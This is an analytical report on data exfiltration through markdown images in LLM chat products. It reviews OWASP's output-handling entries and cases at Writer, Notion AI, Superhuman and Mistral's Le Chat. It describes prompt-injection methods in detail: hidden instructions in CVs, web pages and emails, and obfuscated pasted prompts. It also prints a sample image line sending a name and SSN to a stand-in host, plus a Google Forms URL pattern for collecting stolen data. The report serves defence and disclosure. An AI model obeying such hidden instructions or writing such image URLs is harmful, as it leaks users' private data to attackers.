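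OWASP doesn't mention attackers in its definition, so an application can have the flaw even when the model writes exactly what the user asked for. In one of OWASP's scenarios, a user asks a chat feature to delete every table in a database, the model writes the command, and the application runs it without checking it.

The 2023 entry gives the browser and the command shell as common examples and includes a database in its scenarios. The 2025 entry adds file paths and email templates. In a hiring assistant, the model might write a database query to find candidates in Leeds, choose the file name for a saved summary, or fill in a rejection email. A file name that contains `../` can make the application access files outside the intended folder, while a browser would display the same characters harmlessly. OWASP therefore recommends "context-aware output encoding", which means making special characters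 harmless in the particular place where the text will be used.

OWASP also lists what an attacker can achieve. In the browser, the attacker may run a script or use cross-site request forgery, which makes the user's browser send an unwanted request to a site where the user is logged in. On the company's servers, the attacker may gain extra privileges, run code, or get a server to make requests for them. The list does not include leaking data through an ordinary image, although OWASP's definition is broad enough to cover it.

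### One leak under five headings

OWASP has separate entries for problems that can occur in the same attack. Five of these entries describe different parts of the image leak that sends Jane Doe's social security number to the candidate.

| OWASP category | What it describes in this leak | What would help at that point |
|---|---|---|
| Prompt injection | The hidden line in the CV changes what the model writes | Training the model to ignore instructions in documents |
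| Excessive agency | The assistant can look up applicants the recruiter didn't ask about | Limiting which records it can fetch |
| Improper output handling | The application turns the model's text into an image that loads by itself | Refusing images from unknown hosts |
| Sensitive information disclosure | Jane Doe's number reaches someone with no right to it | Keeping the number out of the conversation |
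| Misinformation | The caption "Salary chart" describes a chart that doesn't exist | Checking the reply against its sources |

Improper output handling concerns how an application uses the model's output, whereas prompt injection concerns the model's input. An application can have either problem without the other.

Sensitive information disclosure is defined by its result. As Respan summarises the 2026 entry, it covers any channel through which confidential data reaches someone without authorisation, including logs, tool-call arguments and even the timing of replies. An image address can be such a channel, and so can an ordinary reply that shows one applicant's record to another, even with no attacker and no rendering flaw.

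Excessive agency is harder to apply. OWASP attributes it to giving a model more functions, permissions or independence than its task requires. In the original version of the example, the recruiter had put Jane Doe's record into the conversation, so the assistant had no excess permission. The category fits better if the assistant searched the whole applicant database on its own. An open renderer is arguably also a form of excessive agency, because it lets a model with no tools contact any server on the internet. HackerDNA's *OWASP LLM Top 10 (2026)*, a guide from a company that runs hacking courses, lists "rendering fetched resources" among the ways an agent can communicate with the outside world.

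Improper output handling and excessive agency can be closely related. In the first scenario of OWASP's 2025 entry, a chatbot passes its reply unchecked to an extension that also has administrative functions, causing the extension to shut down for maintenance. The integrator could prevent this by checking the reply or by removing the administrative functions from the extension.

Misinformation is the category that fits the leak least well, because the leak doesn't depend on the summary being false. The 2025 entry on output handling still contrasts it with "overreliance", the 2023 name for misinformation, even though the 2025 edition renamed that category.

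A diagram in the 2026 edition arranges the ten risks in rings. Eric describes the outer ring as ways into a system, the middle ring as "amplifiers" that make an attack worse, and the centre as the final impacts. Improper output handling is in the middle ring, along with excessive agency, hidden context exposure (leaks of the system prompt and similar material) and weaknesses in the databases that retrieve text for a model. Eric explains that an amplifier can turn an injection that only makes the model's output wrong into one that sends data out.

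### The 2025 advice and the image leak

The second scenario in the 2025 entry closely resembles image exfiltration. A user asks a tool to summarise an article, and the article's web page contains instructions to collect sensitive material from the page or the conversation. The model then encodes the data and sends it to an attacker's server "without any output validation or filtering". The 2023 entry has the same scenario.

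OWASP doesn't explain how the data is sent. The request could come from a tool or from the user's browser. The entry's reference list includes an article about Samoilenko's 2023 attack, with a title about markdown images stealing chat data, so OWASP's contributors evidently knew that images could be used this way. But the main text mentions markdown only as a way for code to run.

OWASP recommended three mitigations in 2023 and seven in 2025, and none of the seven mentions images. An integrator could apply all seven to Jane Doe's record and still leak data.

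OWASP's advice to validate responses concerns text sent to "backend functions", meaning code on the company's servers, but the image goes to the browser. Parameterised queries, which keep values separate from database commands, protect only the database. Logging may help someone discover the leak afterwards. OWASP also refers readers to its Application Security Verification Standard, a much longer list of controls that developers can check one by one.

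Encoding, or escaping, looks more promising, and OWASP recommends it twice, but the result depends on when the integrator applies it. Suppose the integrator's code encodes the model's reply before the markdown renderer receives it, and the reply contains this line:

`![Salary chart](https://images.example/p.png?d=Jane%20Doe%2C%20123-45-6789)`

HTML encoding doesn't change any characters in the line, so the renderer still turns it into a working image. If the code encodes the finished HTML instead, the browser doesn't load the image, but the recruiter sees raw tags around every heading and list. An integrator who wants formatted replies will probably encode before rendering or use a sanitiser, but DOMPurify's default settings also keep the image.

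OWASP's remaining recommendation is a strict content security policy (CSP) "to mitigate the risk of XSS attacks". A policy that restricts only scripts, like the rule in Electron's documentation, would follow that advice but would not block the image. Even a rule that restricts images fails if it permits the wrong host. Willison (2026) traces a leak in the email product Superhuman to a CSP rule that permitted images from docs.google.com, where an attacker could collect data with a Google form.

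A company that used OWASP's seven mitigations as a checklist would find no item about testing an ordinary image. The entry is short and has to cover browsers, shells, databases and email, so it can't give detailed instructions for each. A reader who asks how a summary could reach a stranger's server could still infer the right remedy from the phrase about missing "validation or filtering".

Parameterised queries also don't prevent the scenario about deleted tables. They work when the developer writes the command and the user supplies the values, but in that scenario the model writes the whole command. The application therefore needs a check on which commands it will run, or a database account that can't delete tables.

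### What the 2026 edition added

Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026) reports that the 2026 edition's entry now covers renderers on the user's device that automatically fetch outside resources mentioned in model output, and that OWASP treats this as a way to exfiltrate data. HackerDNA's account of the entry specifies markdown images. Samoilenko demonstrated the leak more than three years before the 2026 edition.

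The new edition also adds terminals and code editors. A terminal is a text window for typing commands. Certain character sequences, called ANSI escape sequences, make it change the colour of text, move the cursor or erase a line. If a coding assistant reads a hostile file, its reply could contain a sequence that erases a warning or replaces the command the developer sees with a different one. A sanitiser made for HTML would not check for these sequences.

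Respan also lists the insecure code that AI assistants produce in large quantities as an addition. This is more of an expansion than a new subject, since the 2025 entry already had a scenario about generated code. OWASP generally widened existing entries instead of creating new ones because, according to Respan, small new categories would have fragmented the list. The document grew from 46 pages to 122, according to Citadelo's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026).

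HackerDNA advises testers to follow a reply to every place it can reach, such as a browser, log viewer, code editor, email template or database query, and to test each one with content it interprets. Examples include a markdown image for a browser or log viewer and an escape sequence for a terminal.

Naming the image route is not the same as telling integrators to restrict image hosts. Eric mentions two mitigations from the 2026 entry, encoding output for its destination and using parameterised queries, but neither would reliably stop the image in the hiring assistant. Another part of the document recommends sandboxing the model to limit its network access, which, as Infosecurity Magazine explains, makes it harder for an attacker to send data out. Sandboxing can block a request from the company's server, but the image request comes from the recruiter's browser, which is outside the sandbox.

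The project leads, Steve Wilson and Rock Lambros (named in Cyber Security News' *OWASP Releases GenAI LLM Top 10 2026*), give broader advice that does apply to rendering. They tell developers to "Stop trying to build a model that cannot be fooled" and to design the surrounding system so that a fooled model does little damage. For prompt injection, OWASP recommends limiting what the model may do and what its outputs may reach. A renderer that blocks requests to unknown hosts directly limits what the outputs may reach, so following OWASP's advice on prompt injection, its first-ranked risk, depends partly on fixing improper output handling, its tenth.

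### How OWASP ranked the 2026 list

Respan reports that OWASP ranked the entries in earlier editions by a vote among practitioners. For 2026, OWASP also collected 7,714 incidents from public vulnerability databases and a database of harms caused by AI. Of these, 6,639 (86%) had enough detail to classify.

The vote counted for about 75% of the ranking and the incidents for 25%. OWASP weighted the vote heavily so that one year of imperfect incident data could not overturn the voters' judgement.

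Sensitive information disclosure and excessive agency ranked similarly in the vote and the incident record, and excessive agency rose from sixth to third. The rankings differed most for misinformation, which was near the bottom in the vote and near the top in the incident record. Prompt injection would have dropped out of the top ten based on incidents alone, but it stayed first because of the vote.

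OWASP attributes the low count for prompt injection to a "defense effect", in which companies work hard to stop it, so fewer successful attacks reach public databases. Advait Patel, a security engineer interviewed by ReversingLabs, adds that the vote reflects what practitioners worry about, while the incidents show what has caused harm. The defense effect is plausible but hard to test with the same data, because a low count could also mean that attacks are rare, or that victims don't notice or report them.

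Improper output handling fell from fifth to tenth, further than any other entry. All five risks that ranked below it in 2025 now rank above it.

Invicti's explanation is that the risks now ranked above improper output handling became more urgent, "not that the risk itself diminished". That fits excessive agency, unbounded consumption (running up a company's computing costs) and misinformation, which all rose in the ranking. It fits less well for hidden context exposure and weaknesses in retrieval databases, which each fell one place but still overtook output handling. HackerDNA instead says OWASP moved the entry down because web developers already know how to fix the flaw. Neither source gives the number of votes or incidents behind the new position, so both explanations are reasonable guesses.

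If HackerDNA is right, the ranking partly reflects how hard a problem is to fix. A well-known remedy doesn't protect an application until its integrator applies it. Without it, the recruiter's browser will still send Jane Doe's number, as it would have in 2025.

The two positions are hard to compare because fifth place was based on votes alone, while tenth place was based on votes and incidents together. The entry also covers more now, and Mend.io's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* describes it as falling "while widening in scope". To show that the flaw had become less dangerous, someone would have to measure the same thing in both years, such as the share of chat products that load images from any server, or the harm that a typical leak causes.

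The incident count may also depend on how OWASP's classifiers label attacks with several causes. The leak of Jane Doe's record involves an injection, an unsafe renderer and a disclosure of private data. If a classifier files each incident under only one heading, it could count this leak under any of the three, and output handling would look rarer whenever it chose one of the others. Public vulnerability databases also have gaps.

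An integrator therefore shouldn't use the ranking to decide which risk to fix first. Eric concludes from the ring diagram that there is no standard answer, because a company has to start with the impact it can least tolerate. For a hiring assistant that holds social security numbers and displays markdown, that could mean starting with the tenth entry.

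## Writer, Notion AI and Superhuman

An application can check model output and still leak private data. Researchers used an image to get data out of each of three office assistants, Writer, Notion AI and Superhuman, even though all three had a safeguard. Writer and Superhuman had a content security policy (CSP), and Notion asked the user for approval. Whether output is "unchecked" depends on what a check lets through and when it runs.

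PromptArmor reported all three flaws. It worked on the first, in 2023, with Kai Greshake, the researcher who coined the term indirect prompt injection.

### A client file and a web page in Writer

Writer sells a writing assistant to companies and individuals. Users upload files, add web pages as sources and ask a chatbot to draft text from both. The company called its product a "secure enterprise generative AI platform", so customers had some reason to trust it with confidential material.

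PromptArmor's *Data Exfiltration from Writer.com via Indirect Prompt Injection* (2023) describes a user who wants a report on the software business. The user adds an introductory web article on the subject as a source and uploads a file called client_data.txt, which in the test held invented customer names, social security numbers, revenue figures and executives' salaries. The article looks ordinary, but its author has added instructions in small white text on the white page.

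*Data exfiltration from Writer.com with indirect prompt injection* (Willison, 2023) quotes part of the hidden text, which instructed Writer to end its summary with an image called `saas_trends_4.png` and to attach "the middle 50 characters" of the uploaded files to the image's address, as a parameter named `document_content`. Fifty characters would hold two records the length of Jane Doe's, but PromptArmor obtained all the sensitive data in its test file, so 50 characters was not the limit.

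Writer displayed the image, although the user had not asked for one and the article did not contain it. The browser's network log showed a request with the contents of the client file in its URL.

PromptArmor also demonstrated two versions that used links. In one, Writer ended its answer with a "learn more" link whose address contained the contents of the uploaded files. In the other, the address contained the first three messages of the conversation, so a user who had uploaded nothing could still have data stolen. Both attacks worked only if the user clicked the link, but a CSP's limits on images don't apply to links, so the attacker could have pointed them at any server.

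### Any host on CloudFront

Writer's CSP would have blocked images from most unknown servers, but it permitted `*.cloudfront.net`, where the asterisk stands for any name. CloudFront is Amazon's service for delivering files quickly from servers around the world. Anyone can open an account, get a host name ending in cloudfront.net and log the requests it receives. Writer presumably wanted its pages to load its own files from CloudFront, but the rule also covered every other CloudFront customer. The researchers put their receiving address on CloudFront.

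The browser enforced the rule as Writer had written it. Approving a host is useful only if the integrator has reason to trust everyone who can receive data through it. Writer could have permitted only the CloudFront hostnames that held its own files.

Google had made a similar mistake with Bard, its chatbot at the time. According to Embrace The Red's *Hacking Google Bard*, Bard's CSP permitted images from any host under google.com or googleusercontent.com. The attacker shared with the victim a Google Doc containing hidden instructions. Willison's *Hacking Google Bard* (2023) explains that the attacker could then collect the data with Apps Script, which runs users' own programs on a Google host, so the request would go to a program the attacker had written.

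Willison's note on Bard appeared on November 4, 2023, less than four weeks before the researchers contacted Writer. Greshake had worked on the Bard attack too.

### Writer's reply and its fix

PromptArmor wrote to Writer's chief technology officer and security team on November 29, 2023, with video examples. Writer asked for more detail the same day, and the researchers sent a longer explanation with screenshots. They wrote again on December 1. On December 4 they sent a new video with a voiceover and asked about Writer's policy on vulnerability reports.

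Writer replied on December 5, "We do not consider this to be a security issue", saying that real customer accounts could not access websites. PromptArmor answered that paid accounts had the same vulnerability and that it was preparing a public article. It heard nothing more before it published the article on December 15. The article reached fifth place on the discussion site Hacker News that day.

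Willison noted on December 18 that the leak appeared to be fixed. A day later, PromptArmor learned that Writer no longer displayed markdown images or clickable links.

Writer's reason concerned only how the hostile text got in. Even if customer accounts could not open websites, customers could upload a file written by a stranger, and the image would have carried the data out in the same way. PromptArmor is the only source for the claim about paid accounts. Writer's later fix doesn't settle who was right about those accounts, but it does show that Writer decided to close the route within two weeks of calling it a non-issue.

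OpenAI had also been slow to act. PromptArmor pointed out that OpenAI had labelled the same problem in its own system "won't fix". Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* describes a live demonstration in which ChatGPT leaked a consenting victim's conversation. The demonstration took place about eight months after the first report and the day before OpenAI's first mitigation.

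Writer's remedy was to display no images and no clickable links. This is blunt but sound, because nobody has to decide which hosts to trust. However, a user who asks for a report with sources can't click on any of them.

The fix did not cover other ways of displaying model-built content. In July 2026, The Hacker News' *Sandbox Security* reported a separate flaw that had already been patched. A link to an agent preview could expose a Writer user's session token and let an outsider take over the account.

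### An edit that took effect before approval

Notion is a workspace application for documents, notes and databases, and Notion AI can edit those documents. PromptArmor tested Notion AI with a task much like the recruiter's. The user keeps a hiring tracker in Notion, uploads a candidate's CV and asks for help updating the notes. The researchers had hidden instructions in the CV, between the candidate's job title and contact details, in one-point white type covered by a white square.

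Notion used a language model to scan uploaded files and warn about malicious ones. PromptArmor did not focus on getting past this scan, but noted that an injection could also fool the scanning model and that Notion did not appear to scan other sources, such as web pages. The test therefore shows what could happen after an injection succeeded, but not how often one would succeed.

The hidden text had Notion AI collect everything in the tracker, add it to an address on the researchers' server and insert an image with that address into the document. The steps then ran in this order:

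1. Notion saved the edit to the document.
2. The user's browser requested the image, with the tracker's text in the address.
3. Notion asked whether the user trusted the external site.
4. The user accepted or rejected the edit.

The request sent the researchers salary expectations, comments on candidates, internal details of the role and diversity hiring goals. If the user rejected the edit, Notion could remove the image from the document but not undo the request. The warning showed the full address, including the stolen text, so an attentive user could have recognised the leak just after it happened.

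Output counts as displayed once the application gives it to the browser in a form the browser will act on, even if the user hasn't read it, approved it or scrolled down to it. A suggested edit is therefore displayed if the page already contains its image, and so is the first half of a reply that is still streaming. Notion considered the edit still a proposal, but browsers treat an image in a proposal like any other image. In line with this definition, Varonis recommends sanitising output at the moment of rendering, following its work on Copilot.

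An approval screen can itself cause the leak if it loads the image in the proposed edit. To avoid this, the application can show the image's address as plain text, or an empty box, until the user agrees. A tester can check for this by triggering the approval prompt, leaving it unanswered and looking at the log of the server named in the image address. If the log shows a request, the application loaded the image without waiting for approval.

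The drafting assistant in Notion Mail had a related flaw. If a user asked for a draft based on two Notion pages, one written by an attacker, the attacker's page could make the assistant put text from the other page into an image address in the draft. Deleting the draft without sending it would not prevent the leak, because the browser would already have requested the image. PromptArmor considered the risk smaller here because the assistant appeared to read only the Notion material the user mentioned.

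### Two rounds of fixes at Notion

Notion had dealt with a different leak a few months earlier. In September 2025, a day after the company released Notion 3.0, Abi Raghuram reported that its AI agent could send data out through web search. Willison, in *The Hidden Risk in Notion 3.0 AI Agents*, describes a PDF whose hidden text made the agent read a list of clients, join their names and annual revenue into one string, and put that string into a web address for its search tool.

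Notion responded by upgrading its detection systems to catch more kinds of injection, including text hidden in attachments, according to The Decoder's *Notion AI agents get security update after potential data leak* (2025). Notion's help page on prompt injection also lists settings that let administrators turn off web search or require permission before an agent visits a website. On the same page, Notion promises "User approval needed for any suspicious links".

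These measures made hostile text easier to spot and the search tool easier to control. They left the image route open, because the request to approve a suspicious address appeared only after the browser had used that address.

PromptArmor reported the image flaw on December 24, 2025, through HackerOne, a company that receives and sorts vulnerability reports for other companies. Notion accepted reports only through HackerOne. HackerOne asked for a different format, and PromptArmor supplied it the same day. Five days later PromptArmor learned that the report had been closed as "Not Applicable".

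PromptArmor published its findings on January 7, 2026. Notion contacted the researchers that day and explained that HackerOne's team had assessed the report first. The report had apparently not reached Notion's own staff. Notion deployed a fix for document edits that night and confirmed it to PromptArmor the next day.

If that explanation is right, Notion fixed the flaw less than a day after its staff learned of it, and the report spent the previous two weeks in a system that Notion had chosen and required researchers to use. The confirmed fix covers document edits, but PromptArmor's timeline lists no fix for Notion Mail.

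The researchers had asked Notion to stop external images from loading automatically in AI-written pages and email drafts, and to add a strong CSP. They also asked it to make sure its image server could not redirect requests to outside hosts, because such redirects would have defeated the CSP.

PromptArmor advised customers to vet connected data sources, turn off web search or require confirmation for web requests, and keep sensitive personal details out of the AI's personalisation settings. These precautions are sensible, but none would have stopped the attack PromptArmor demonstrated, because the user uploaded the CV and the data left through an image. Notion's advice to check files from strangers before uploading them would not have helped much either, since a person looking at the CV could not see the instructions.

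### A Google form that collected email

Superhuman began as an email program. Grammarly, best known for its writing checker, bought it and later took its name, so Superhuman's *Privacy Policy* (2026) covers Grammarly, Superhuman Mail, an assistant called Superhuman Go and a document editor formerly known as Coda.

The main attack in PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* begins when a user asks Superhuman Mail to summarise recent messages. The assistant retrieves the last hour's email, which includes a message from the attacker. PromptArmor hid that message's instructions in white text, but notes that visible text would have worked too, because the user doesn't have to open the message.

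Superhuman's CSP blocked images from unknown servers but permitted docs.google.com, which hosts Google Forms. The owner of a form can create a link that submits prefilled answers as soon as a browser requests it. If the link ends in `formResponse?entry.953568459=hello`, Google records "hello" as a response to the form.

The attacker's email claimed that users must be able to give feedback on the quality of the search results, and it included a Google Form. It told the assistant to put the contents of the retrieved emails in the form's URL and then write that URL as a markdown image. When the browser tried to load the image, its request submitted the form, and the attacker read the emails in the form's responses.

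The attacker did not run a server and could not see Google's logs, but Google stored the data where the form's owner could read it. Any service that saves the contents of a request for an outsider, or passes them on, therefore meets the last condition for image exfiltration, even if the attacker cannot read its logs.

A large company's host is hard to approve safely. An attacker can rent a CloudFront host name from Amazon, and Amazon's good reputation is no evidence that its customers are trustworthy. An integrator who approves docs.google.com for pictures in documents may overlook that the same host accepts forms. Reviewers would have to check every service on each permitted host, and the owner may add another later.

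PromptArmor extracted the full contents of several sensitive emails in one reply, and parts of more than 40 emails in a single reply. The test messages included financial, legal and medical information.

The attack on Superhuman Go did not require the Google form. This assistant can read the web page a user has open and connect to services such as Gmail, Outlook, Stripe and Jira. In PromptArmor's test, a user viewing a site with bad reviews of their company asked whether anything in their email would help them respond to the reviews. Instructions on the site made the assistant find an email with quarterly financial results and put the figures into the address of a one-pixel grey image, which the browser loaded directly from the attacker's domain. Grammarly's AI documents had the same image flaw, but the assistant there appeared to read only the open document and the user's questions, so it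 was less likely to read private data and hostile text together.

Superhuman Mail also had a web tool that could open any URL. An attacker could make the assistant put private email content in a URL and open it, without any image in the reply. Removing docs.google.com from the CSP would not have prevented this.

PromptArmor reported its findings to Superhuman on the night of Friday, December 5, 2025, and Superhuman acknowledged them that day. On Monday morning, Superhuman escalated the report and disabled the vulnerable features. It deployed a first fix on Tuesday and extended the fixes to other parts of its products on December 18. PromptArmor sent more findings on January 5, 2026, and Superhuman released more patches on January 11. PromptArmor published its findings the next day, by agreement with Superhuman.

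In *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails*, Willison (2026) also credits Superhuman with treating the report as a high-priority incident. Disabling the features first was a good decision because it protected users before the company understood every route. The later findings suggest that understanding them all would have taken weeks.

### Causes, responses and remedies

| | Writer | Notion AI | Superhuman Mail |
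|---|---|---|---|
| Source of the hostile text | A web page added as a source | An uploaded CV | An email in the inbox |
| Existing check | CSP | Approval question | CSP |
| Why the check failed | It permitted every CloudFront host | It appeared after the browser had requested the image | It permitted a host that accepts form submissions |
| First response | Not a security issue | Report closed as not applicable, apparently by HackerOne | Acknowledged the same day |
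| Remedy | Stopped displaying images and clickable links | Fixed document edits | Disabled the features, then repaired them |
| Report to first known protection | About 20 days | 14 days | 3 days |
| Publication | Before the fix | Before the fix | After the fixes |

Superhuman's CSP had much the same weakness as Writer's, two years after the Writer case became public, so evidently not every integrator had learned from that case to examine its permitted hosts. Publicity may have sped up individual repairs, since Writer and Notion both acted within days of publication. The link is clearer for Notion, which contacted the researchers on the day the article appeared, than for Writer, which has not explained why it changed its product.

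Most of this evidence comes from PromptArmor, which sells continuous monitoring of the AI products that companies buy and advertises this service beneath its reports. Readers can also ask to unlock its risk report on Notion. PromptArmor benefits commercially when buyers worry about their vendors, and it can choose which flaws to publicise. Three published cases therefore can't show how common the flaw is among business assistants.

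PromptArmor's commercial interest is less of a reason to doubt its technical findings, because it published screenshots of the requests and of the data that arrived, and all three vendors changed their products afterwards. Its praise for Superhuman also suggests that it was not trying to make every vendor look careless. Its accounts of its correspondence with the vendors are harder to check, especially for Writer, whose side is known mainly from one sentence PromptArmor quoted. The attacks were demonstrations, and PromptArmor does not report that any of the vendors' customers lost data through them.

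## Mistral's Le Chat

PromptArmor's demonstrations showed that three office assistants could leak data, but not how often an attempt would succeed. *Imprompter* (Fu, Li and colleagues, 2024) measured this for Le Chat, the chatbot of the French AI company Mistral. The researchers tried disguised prompts on the live service and recorded how often it produced an image and how much personal data the image's address contained. Mistral changed Le Chat in September 2024, so the results describe an earlier version.

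### A prompt that the victim pastes

The attacker posts a prompt where people share prompts, perhaps promising that it improves CVs. The prompt looks like a jumble of broken English, punctuation and words from other languages. A user pastes it into a conversation that contains personal details. Le Chat replies with an invisible image, so the reply looks empty. When the browser loads the image, it sends the details to the attacker's server as part of the image's address.

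Fu and colleagues published demonstrations with invented job applicants. In one, the user pasted a cover letter containing a name, phone number, city and email address, followed directly by the hostile prompt. In another, the user first asked which jobs suited a CV and pasted the prompt later in the conversation.

Willison considered disguising the prompt the new part of this work, since leaking data through images was already well known. A plain-English prompt has to tell the model to collect names and card numbers and add them to a web address, so anyone who reads it can see its purpose.

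### How the researchers disguised it

The researchers found the wording by automated search. They started with a readable instruction and repeatedly replaced parts of it, keeping changes that made a model more likely to write the intended image across a set of sample conversations. The search gave extra weight to the fixed characters at the start of the image command, because a small mistake there would keep the browser from loading the image. To make the result harder to read, they excluded English words from some searches. In others, they removed telltale words from a result and searched again.

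The search requires access to a model's weights, the numbers that define it. Mistral published the weights of its Nemo model in July 2024, and Le Chat offered a version that ran on Nemo, so the researchers could develop a prompt on their own copy and try it on the live service. They did the same with the open model GLM-4 and the Chinese chat service ChatGLM. They caution that the method may not work on a closed model that has no similar open one.

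A filter might catch such a prompt by its high perplexity, a measure of how improbable a passage is according to a language model. The prompt used against Le Chat had a perplexity of 7,489, compared with 110 for a plain-English version. But Fu and colleagues note that harmless prompts tuned by software can also have high perplexity, so the filter would block some of those too.

### What happened on the live services

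The main test used conversations from WildChat, a collection of real exchanges between people and chatbots. The researchers tested the live services on 25 conversations containing personal details and ran each one only once, because daily limits of around 35 conversations made repeated runs impractical.

They first checked whether each reply contained a correctly formed image command. For the replies that did, they calculated precision (the share of extracted items that were real personal details from the conversation) and recall (the share of the conversation's personal details that the model extracted).

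| Service | Prompt | Image command appeared | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Le Chat | Disguised | 100% | 70.4% | 41.2% |
| Le Chat | Plain English | 44% | 80.2% | 48.2% |
| ChatGLM | Disguised, first version | 96% | 0% | 0% |
| ChatGLM | Disguised, second version | 92% | 34.7% | 63.0% |
| ChatGLM | Plain English | 40% | 89.1% | 48.1% |

If a conversation with Le Chat contained ten personal details, a typical disguised attack would send the attacker about six items, four of them correct. The attacks also revealed something about the subject of the conversation in 88% of cases, according to OpenAI's GPT-4o, which the researchers used as a judge.

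The first ChatGLM prompt produced an image in 24 of 25 conversations, but none of the images carried any personal data, so the image command alone is a poor measure of a leak. The same prompt had extracted some details from the researchers' own copy of GLM-4.

On Le Chat, the plain-English prompt had higher precision and recall than the disguised prompt, but only in the 11 conversations where it produced an image. Over all 25 conversations, it would have sent roughly 21% of the personal details, about half as much as the disguised prompt. That is still a serious leak, and an attacker could cause it without access to the model's weights.

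The sample was small. Even if the disguised prompt worked only 89% of the time, it would succeed in all 25 conversations in about one of every 20 such tests. When the researchers tried it on 98 more general conversations, Le Chat produced the image in 89 of them.

They also used those 98 conversations to test prompts that collected keywords instead of personal data. The image command appeared 83 times on Le Chat and 97 times on ChatGLM, with precision of 70.1% and 62.5% respectively. Extraction was somewhat less accurate than on the researchers' own copies of the models. They suggest this was because the live services often replied with code blocks, search results or plots, while the conversations used in the search contained only plain text.

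### The 80% success rate

According to the paper's abstract, the attack on Le Chat had a success rate of "nearly 80%" in an end-to-end evaluation. The closest result for the disguised prompt is a precision of 79.8%, measured on the researchers' own copy of Nemo. Its precision on the live service was 70.4%.

Precision is also an odd measure of success, because it describes the quality of the extracted data. A precision of 80% doesn't mean that four out of five attacks worked. The disguised prompt made Le Chat write the image in all 25 conversations, but the attack missed more than half of the personal details.

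The figure has since circulated without that context. *Mistral Le Chat Agent Security Risks*, an undated profile by the security company Adversa AI, cites the 80% success rate as evidence of a current weakness. The profile refers to an incident from May 2026, so it dates from well over a year after Mistral's fix, which it doesn't mention. It also advises customers to block images from external addresses, which Mistral had already done in 2024.

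### When the user supplies the attack

The attack does not fit neatly into the usual account of indirect prompt injection, because Le Chat received the hostile instructions from its own user rather than from a document or web page. Mistral stressed in its *Changelog* that the attack "required users to willingly copy and paste adversarial prompts" and to give the model personal data.

The need to paste a stranger's prompt made the attack less likely, since people who never do so were safe from this version. It is weaker evidence of consent, because the user agreed to try a prompt they could not read and did not agree to send a phone number to a stranger. Fu and colleagues classify attacks by who intends the harm. Their attack counts as a prompt injection because someone else wrote the instructions and the user was innocent. In a jailbreak, the user is the attacker and tries to get forbidden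 content out of the model.

The user's part in the attack matters for defence because measures that make a model distrust instructions in documents help little if the instructions arrive in the user's own message, which the model is supposed to follow. Samoilenko's 2023 attack on ChatGPT also put its instructions in the user's message, although in that case the user didn't know the copied text contained anything extra.

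Le Chat loaded images from any address the model wrote, regardless of where the model's instructions came from. Mistral added web search to Le Chat on November 18, 2024, about two months after the fix. If Le Chat had still loaded images this way, an attacker might have been able to put the instructions in a web page, without needing the user to paste anything.

### Four days from report to fix

The researchers reported the flaw to Mistral on September 9, 2024. Mistral replied promptly, rated it medium severity and fixed it on September 13 by no longer displaying external images in markdown. The researchers confirmed that the fix worked. Users who repeated the demonstration saw a placeholder instead of the image.

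ChatGLM's developers took longer. The researchers first contacted them on September 18 and tried several channels before getting an answer on October 18. The developers had started working on the problem by then, but the attack still worked on October 21.

Mistral made its change in the display code, so it works however the prompt is disguised. It does not depend on recognising the prompts, though Mistral's description of it as a mitigation against "an obfuscated prompt method" could be read that way. An attacker can word the instruction in countless ways or hide it in a picture. In tests on a small open model that reads images, the researchers' altered pictures produced the image command between 82% and 88% of the time. But every version has to make the model output an image with an outside address, because the browser won't send the data otherwise. The display code can refuse that output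 without recognising the prompt.

The fix works even if the model follows the attacker's instructions. Nemo could still have written the image command, with the same personal details in it, in all 25 test conversations, and the attacker's server would have received nothing.

The fix covers only images. On their own copies of GLM-4 and Meta's Llama 3.1, the researchers found prompts that made the model call a web-browsing tool with words from the conversation in the URL. The prompts produced a correct tool call 79% to 92% of the time.

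Mistral also said that the flaw affected no users and that no data leaked. It did not explain how it reached this conclusion, and outsiders cannot check it. The security company Bitdefender said only that there was no evidence of malicious use.

### A company that controlled both the model and the page

Mistral made both Le Chat and the model behind it, so it could have changed either one. It could have trained Nemo to resist these prompts, but the researchers could then have run their search again on any new weights it published. Changing the front end took four days, and the fix didn't depend on how the model behaved. A company that uses a model through an API can't retrain it, but can make the same change to its own front end.

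The fix also applied only to Le Chat, the only product named in the changelog entry. Outside developers who used Nemo in other chat products had separate renderers, and if those renderers loaded external images, Mistral's change did not protect their users.

Building the model also didn't help Mistral avoid the flaw in the first place. It launched Le Chat in February 2024, ten months after Samoilenko had published a description of the same leak in ChatGPT. A company can understand how a model works and still be careless about what a browser does with its output.

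### A later report about email

Le Chat later gained access to users' email, which let strangers reach the model without the user pasting anything. 0DIN, a programme Mozilla founded in 2024, rewards people for finding flaws in AI models. Its *Mistral LeChat Data Exfiltration via Email Embedded Indirect Prompt Injection* describes how a researcher known as neuroXploit put instructions for the model in an email to someone who used Le Chat with their mailbox. The model then encoded conversation data in base64, and the data went to web addresses the attacker controlled, along with the victim's IP address and browser details.

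0DIN dates the disclosure to August 27, 2025, and published its summary on March 5, 2026. In the public summary, 0DIN doesn't state what carried the data or whether Mistral fixed the flaw. The browser details suggest that the request came from the victim's browser, because a request from Mistral's servers would normally have identified those servers. If so, the carrier could have been a link that the victim clicked, which the 2024 fix did not cover. It could also have been an image, in which case the fix had stopped working or the attacker had found a way around it.

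Mistral's changelog has no entry about this report. The security change it lists for August 27, 2025, the day of the disclosure, addressed a different problem, which Microsoft researchers had found in how Mistral's API streamed replies.

0DIN rated the email attack low severity, one step below Mistral's rating of the 2024 flaw. This is surprising because the victim of the email attack didn't have to paste a suspicious prompt, though the two organisations' ratings may not be comparable. 0DIN also gave the attack the lowest level on its social impact scale, a level it illustrates with getting a model to use inappropriate language. The scale seems better suited to offensive output than to stolen data.

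### Le Chat under its new name

Le Chat is now part of Vibe, which Mistral launched on May 28, 2026. Users kept their conversations and the same web address, according to Mistral's *Le Chat is now Vibe*. Vibe at first kept the old chat as a separate mode, but on September 22 Mistral began merging it with the mode for longer tasks. Enterprise customers have six months to move, according to Mistral's *Vibe*.

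The new product, Vibe, has access to much more private data than the chatbot the researchers tested. It can search Outlook, Google Workspace, SharePoint and Slack, many of which also contain text written by strangers. It also displays charts and dashboards inside the conversation. Mistral promises that Vibe will ask for approval before sensitive actions, but that alone would not stop an image from loading.

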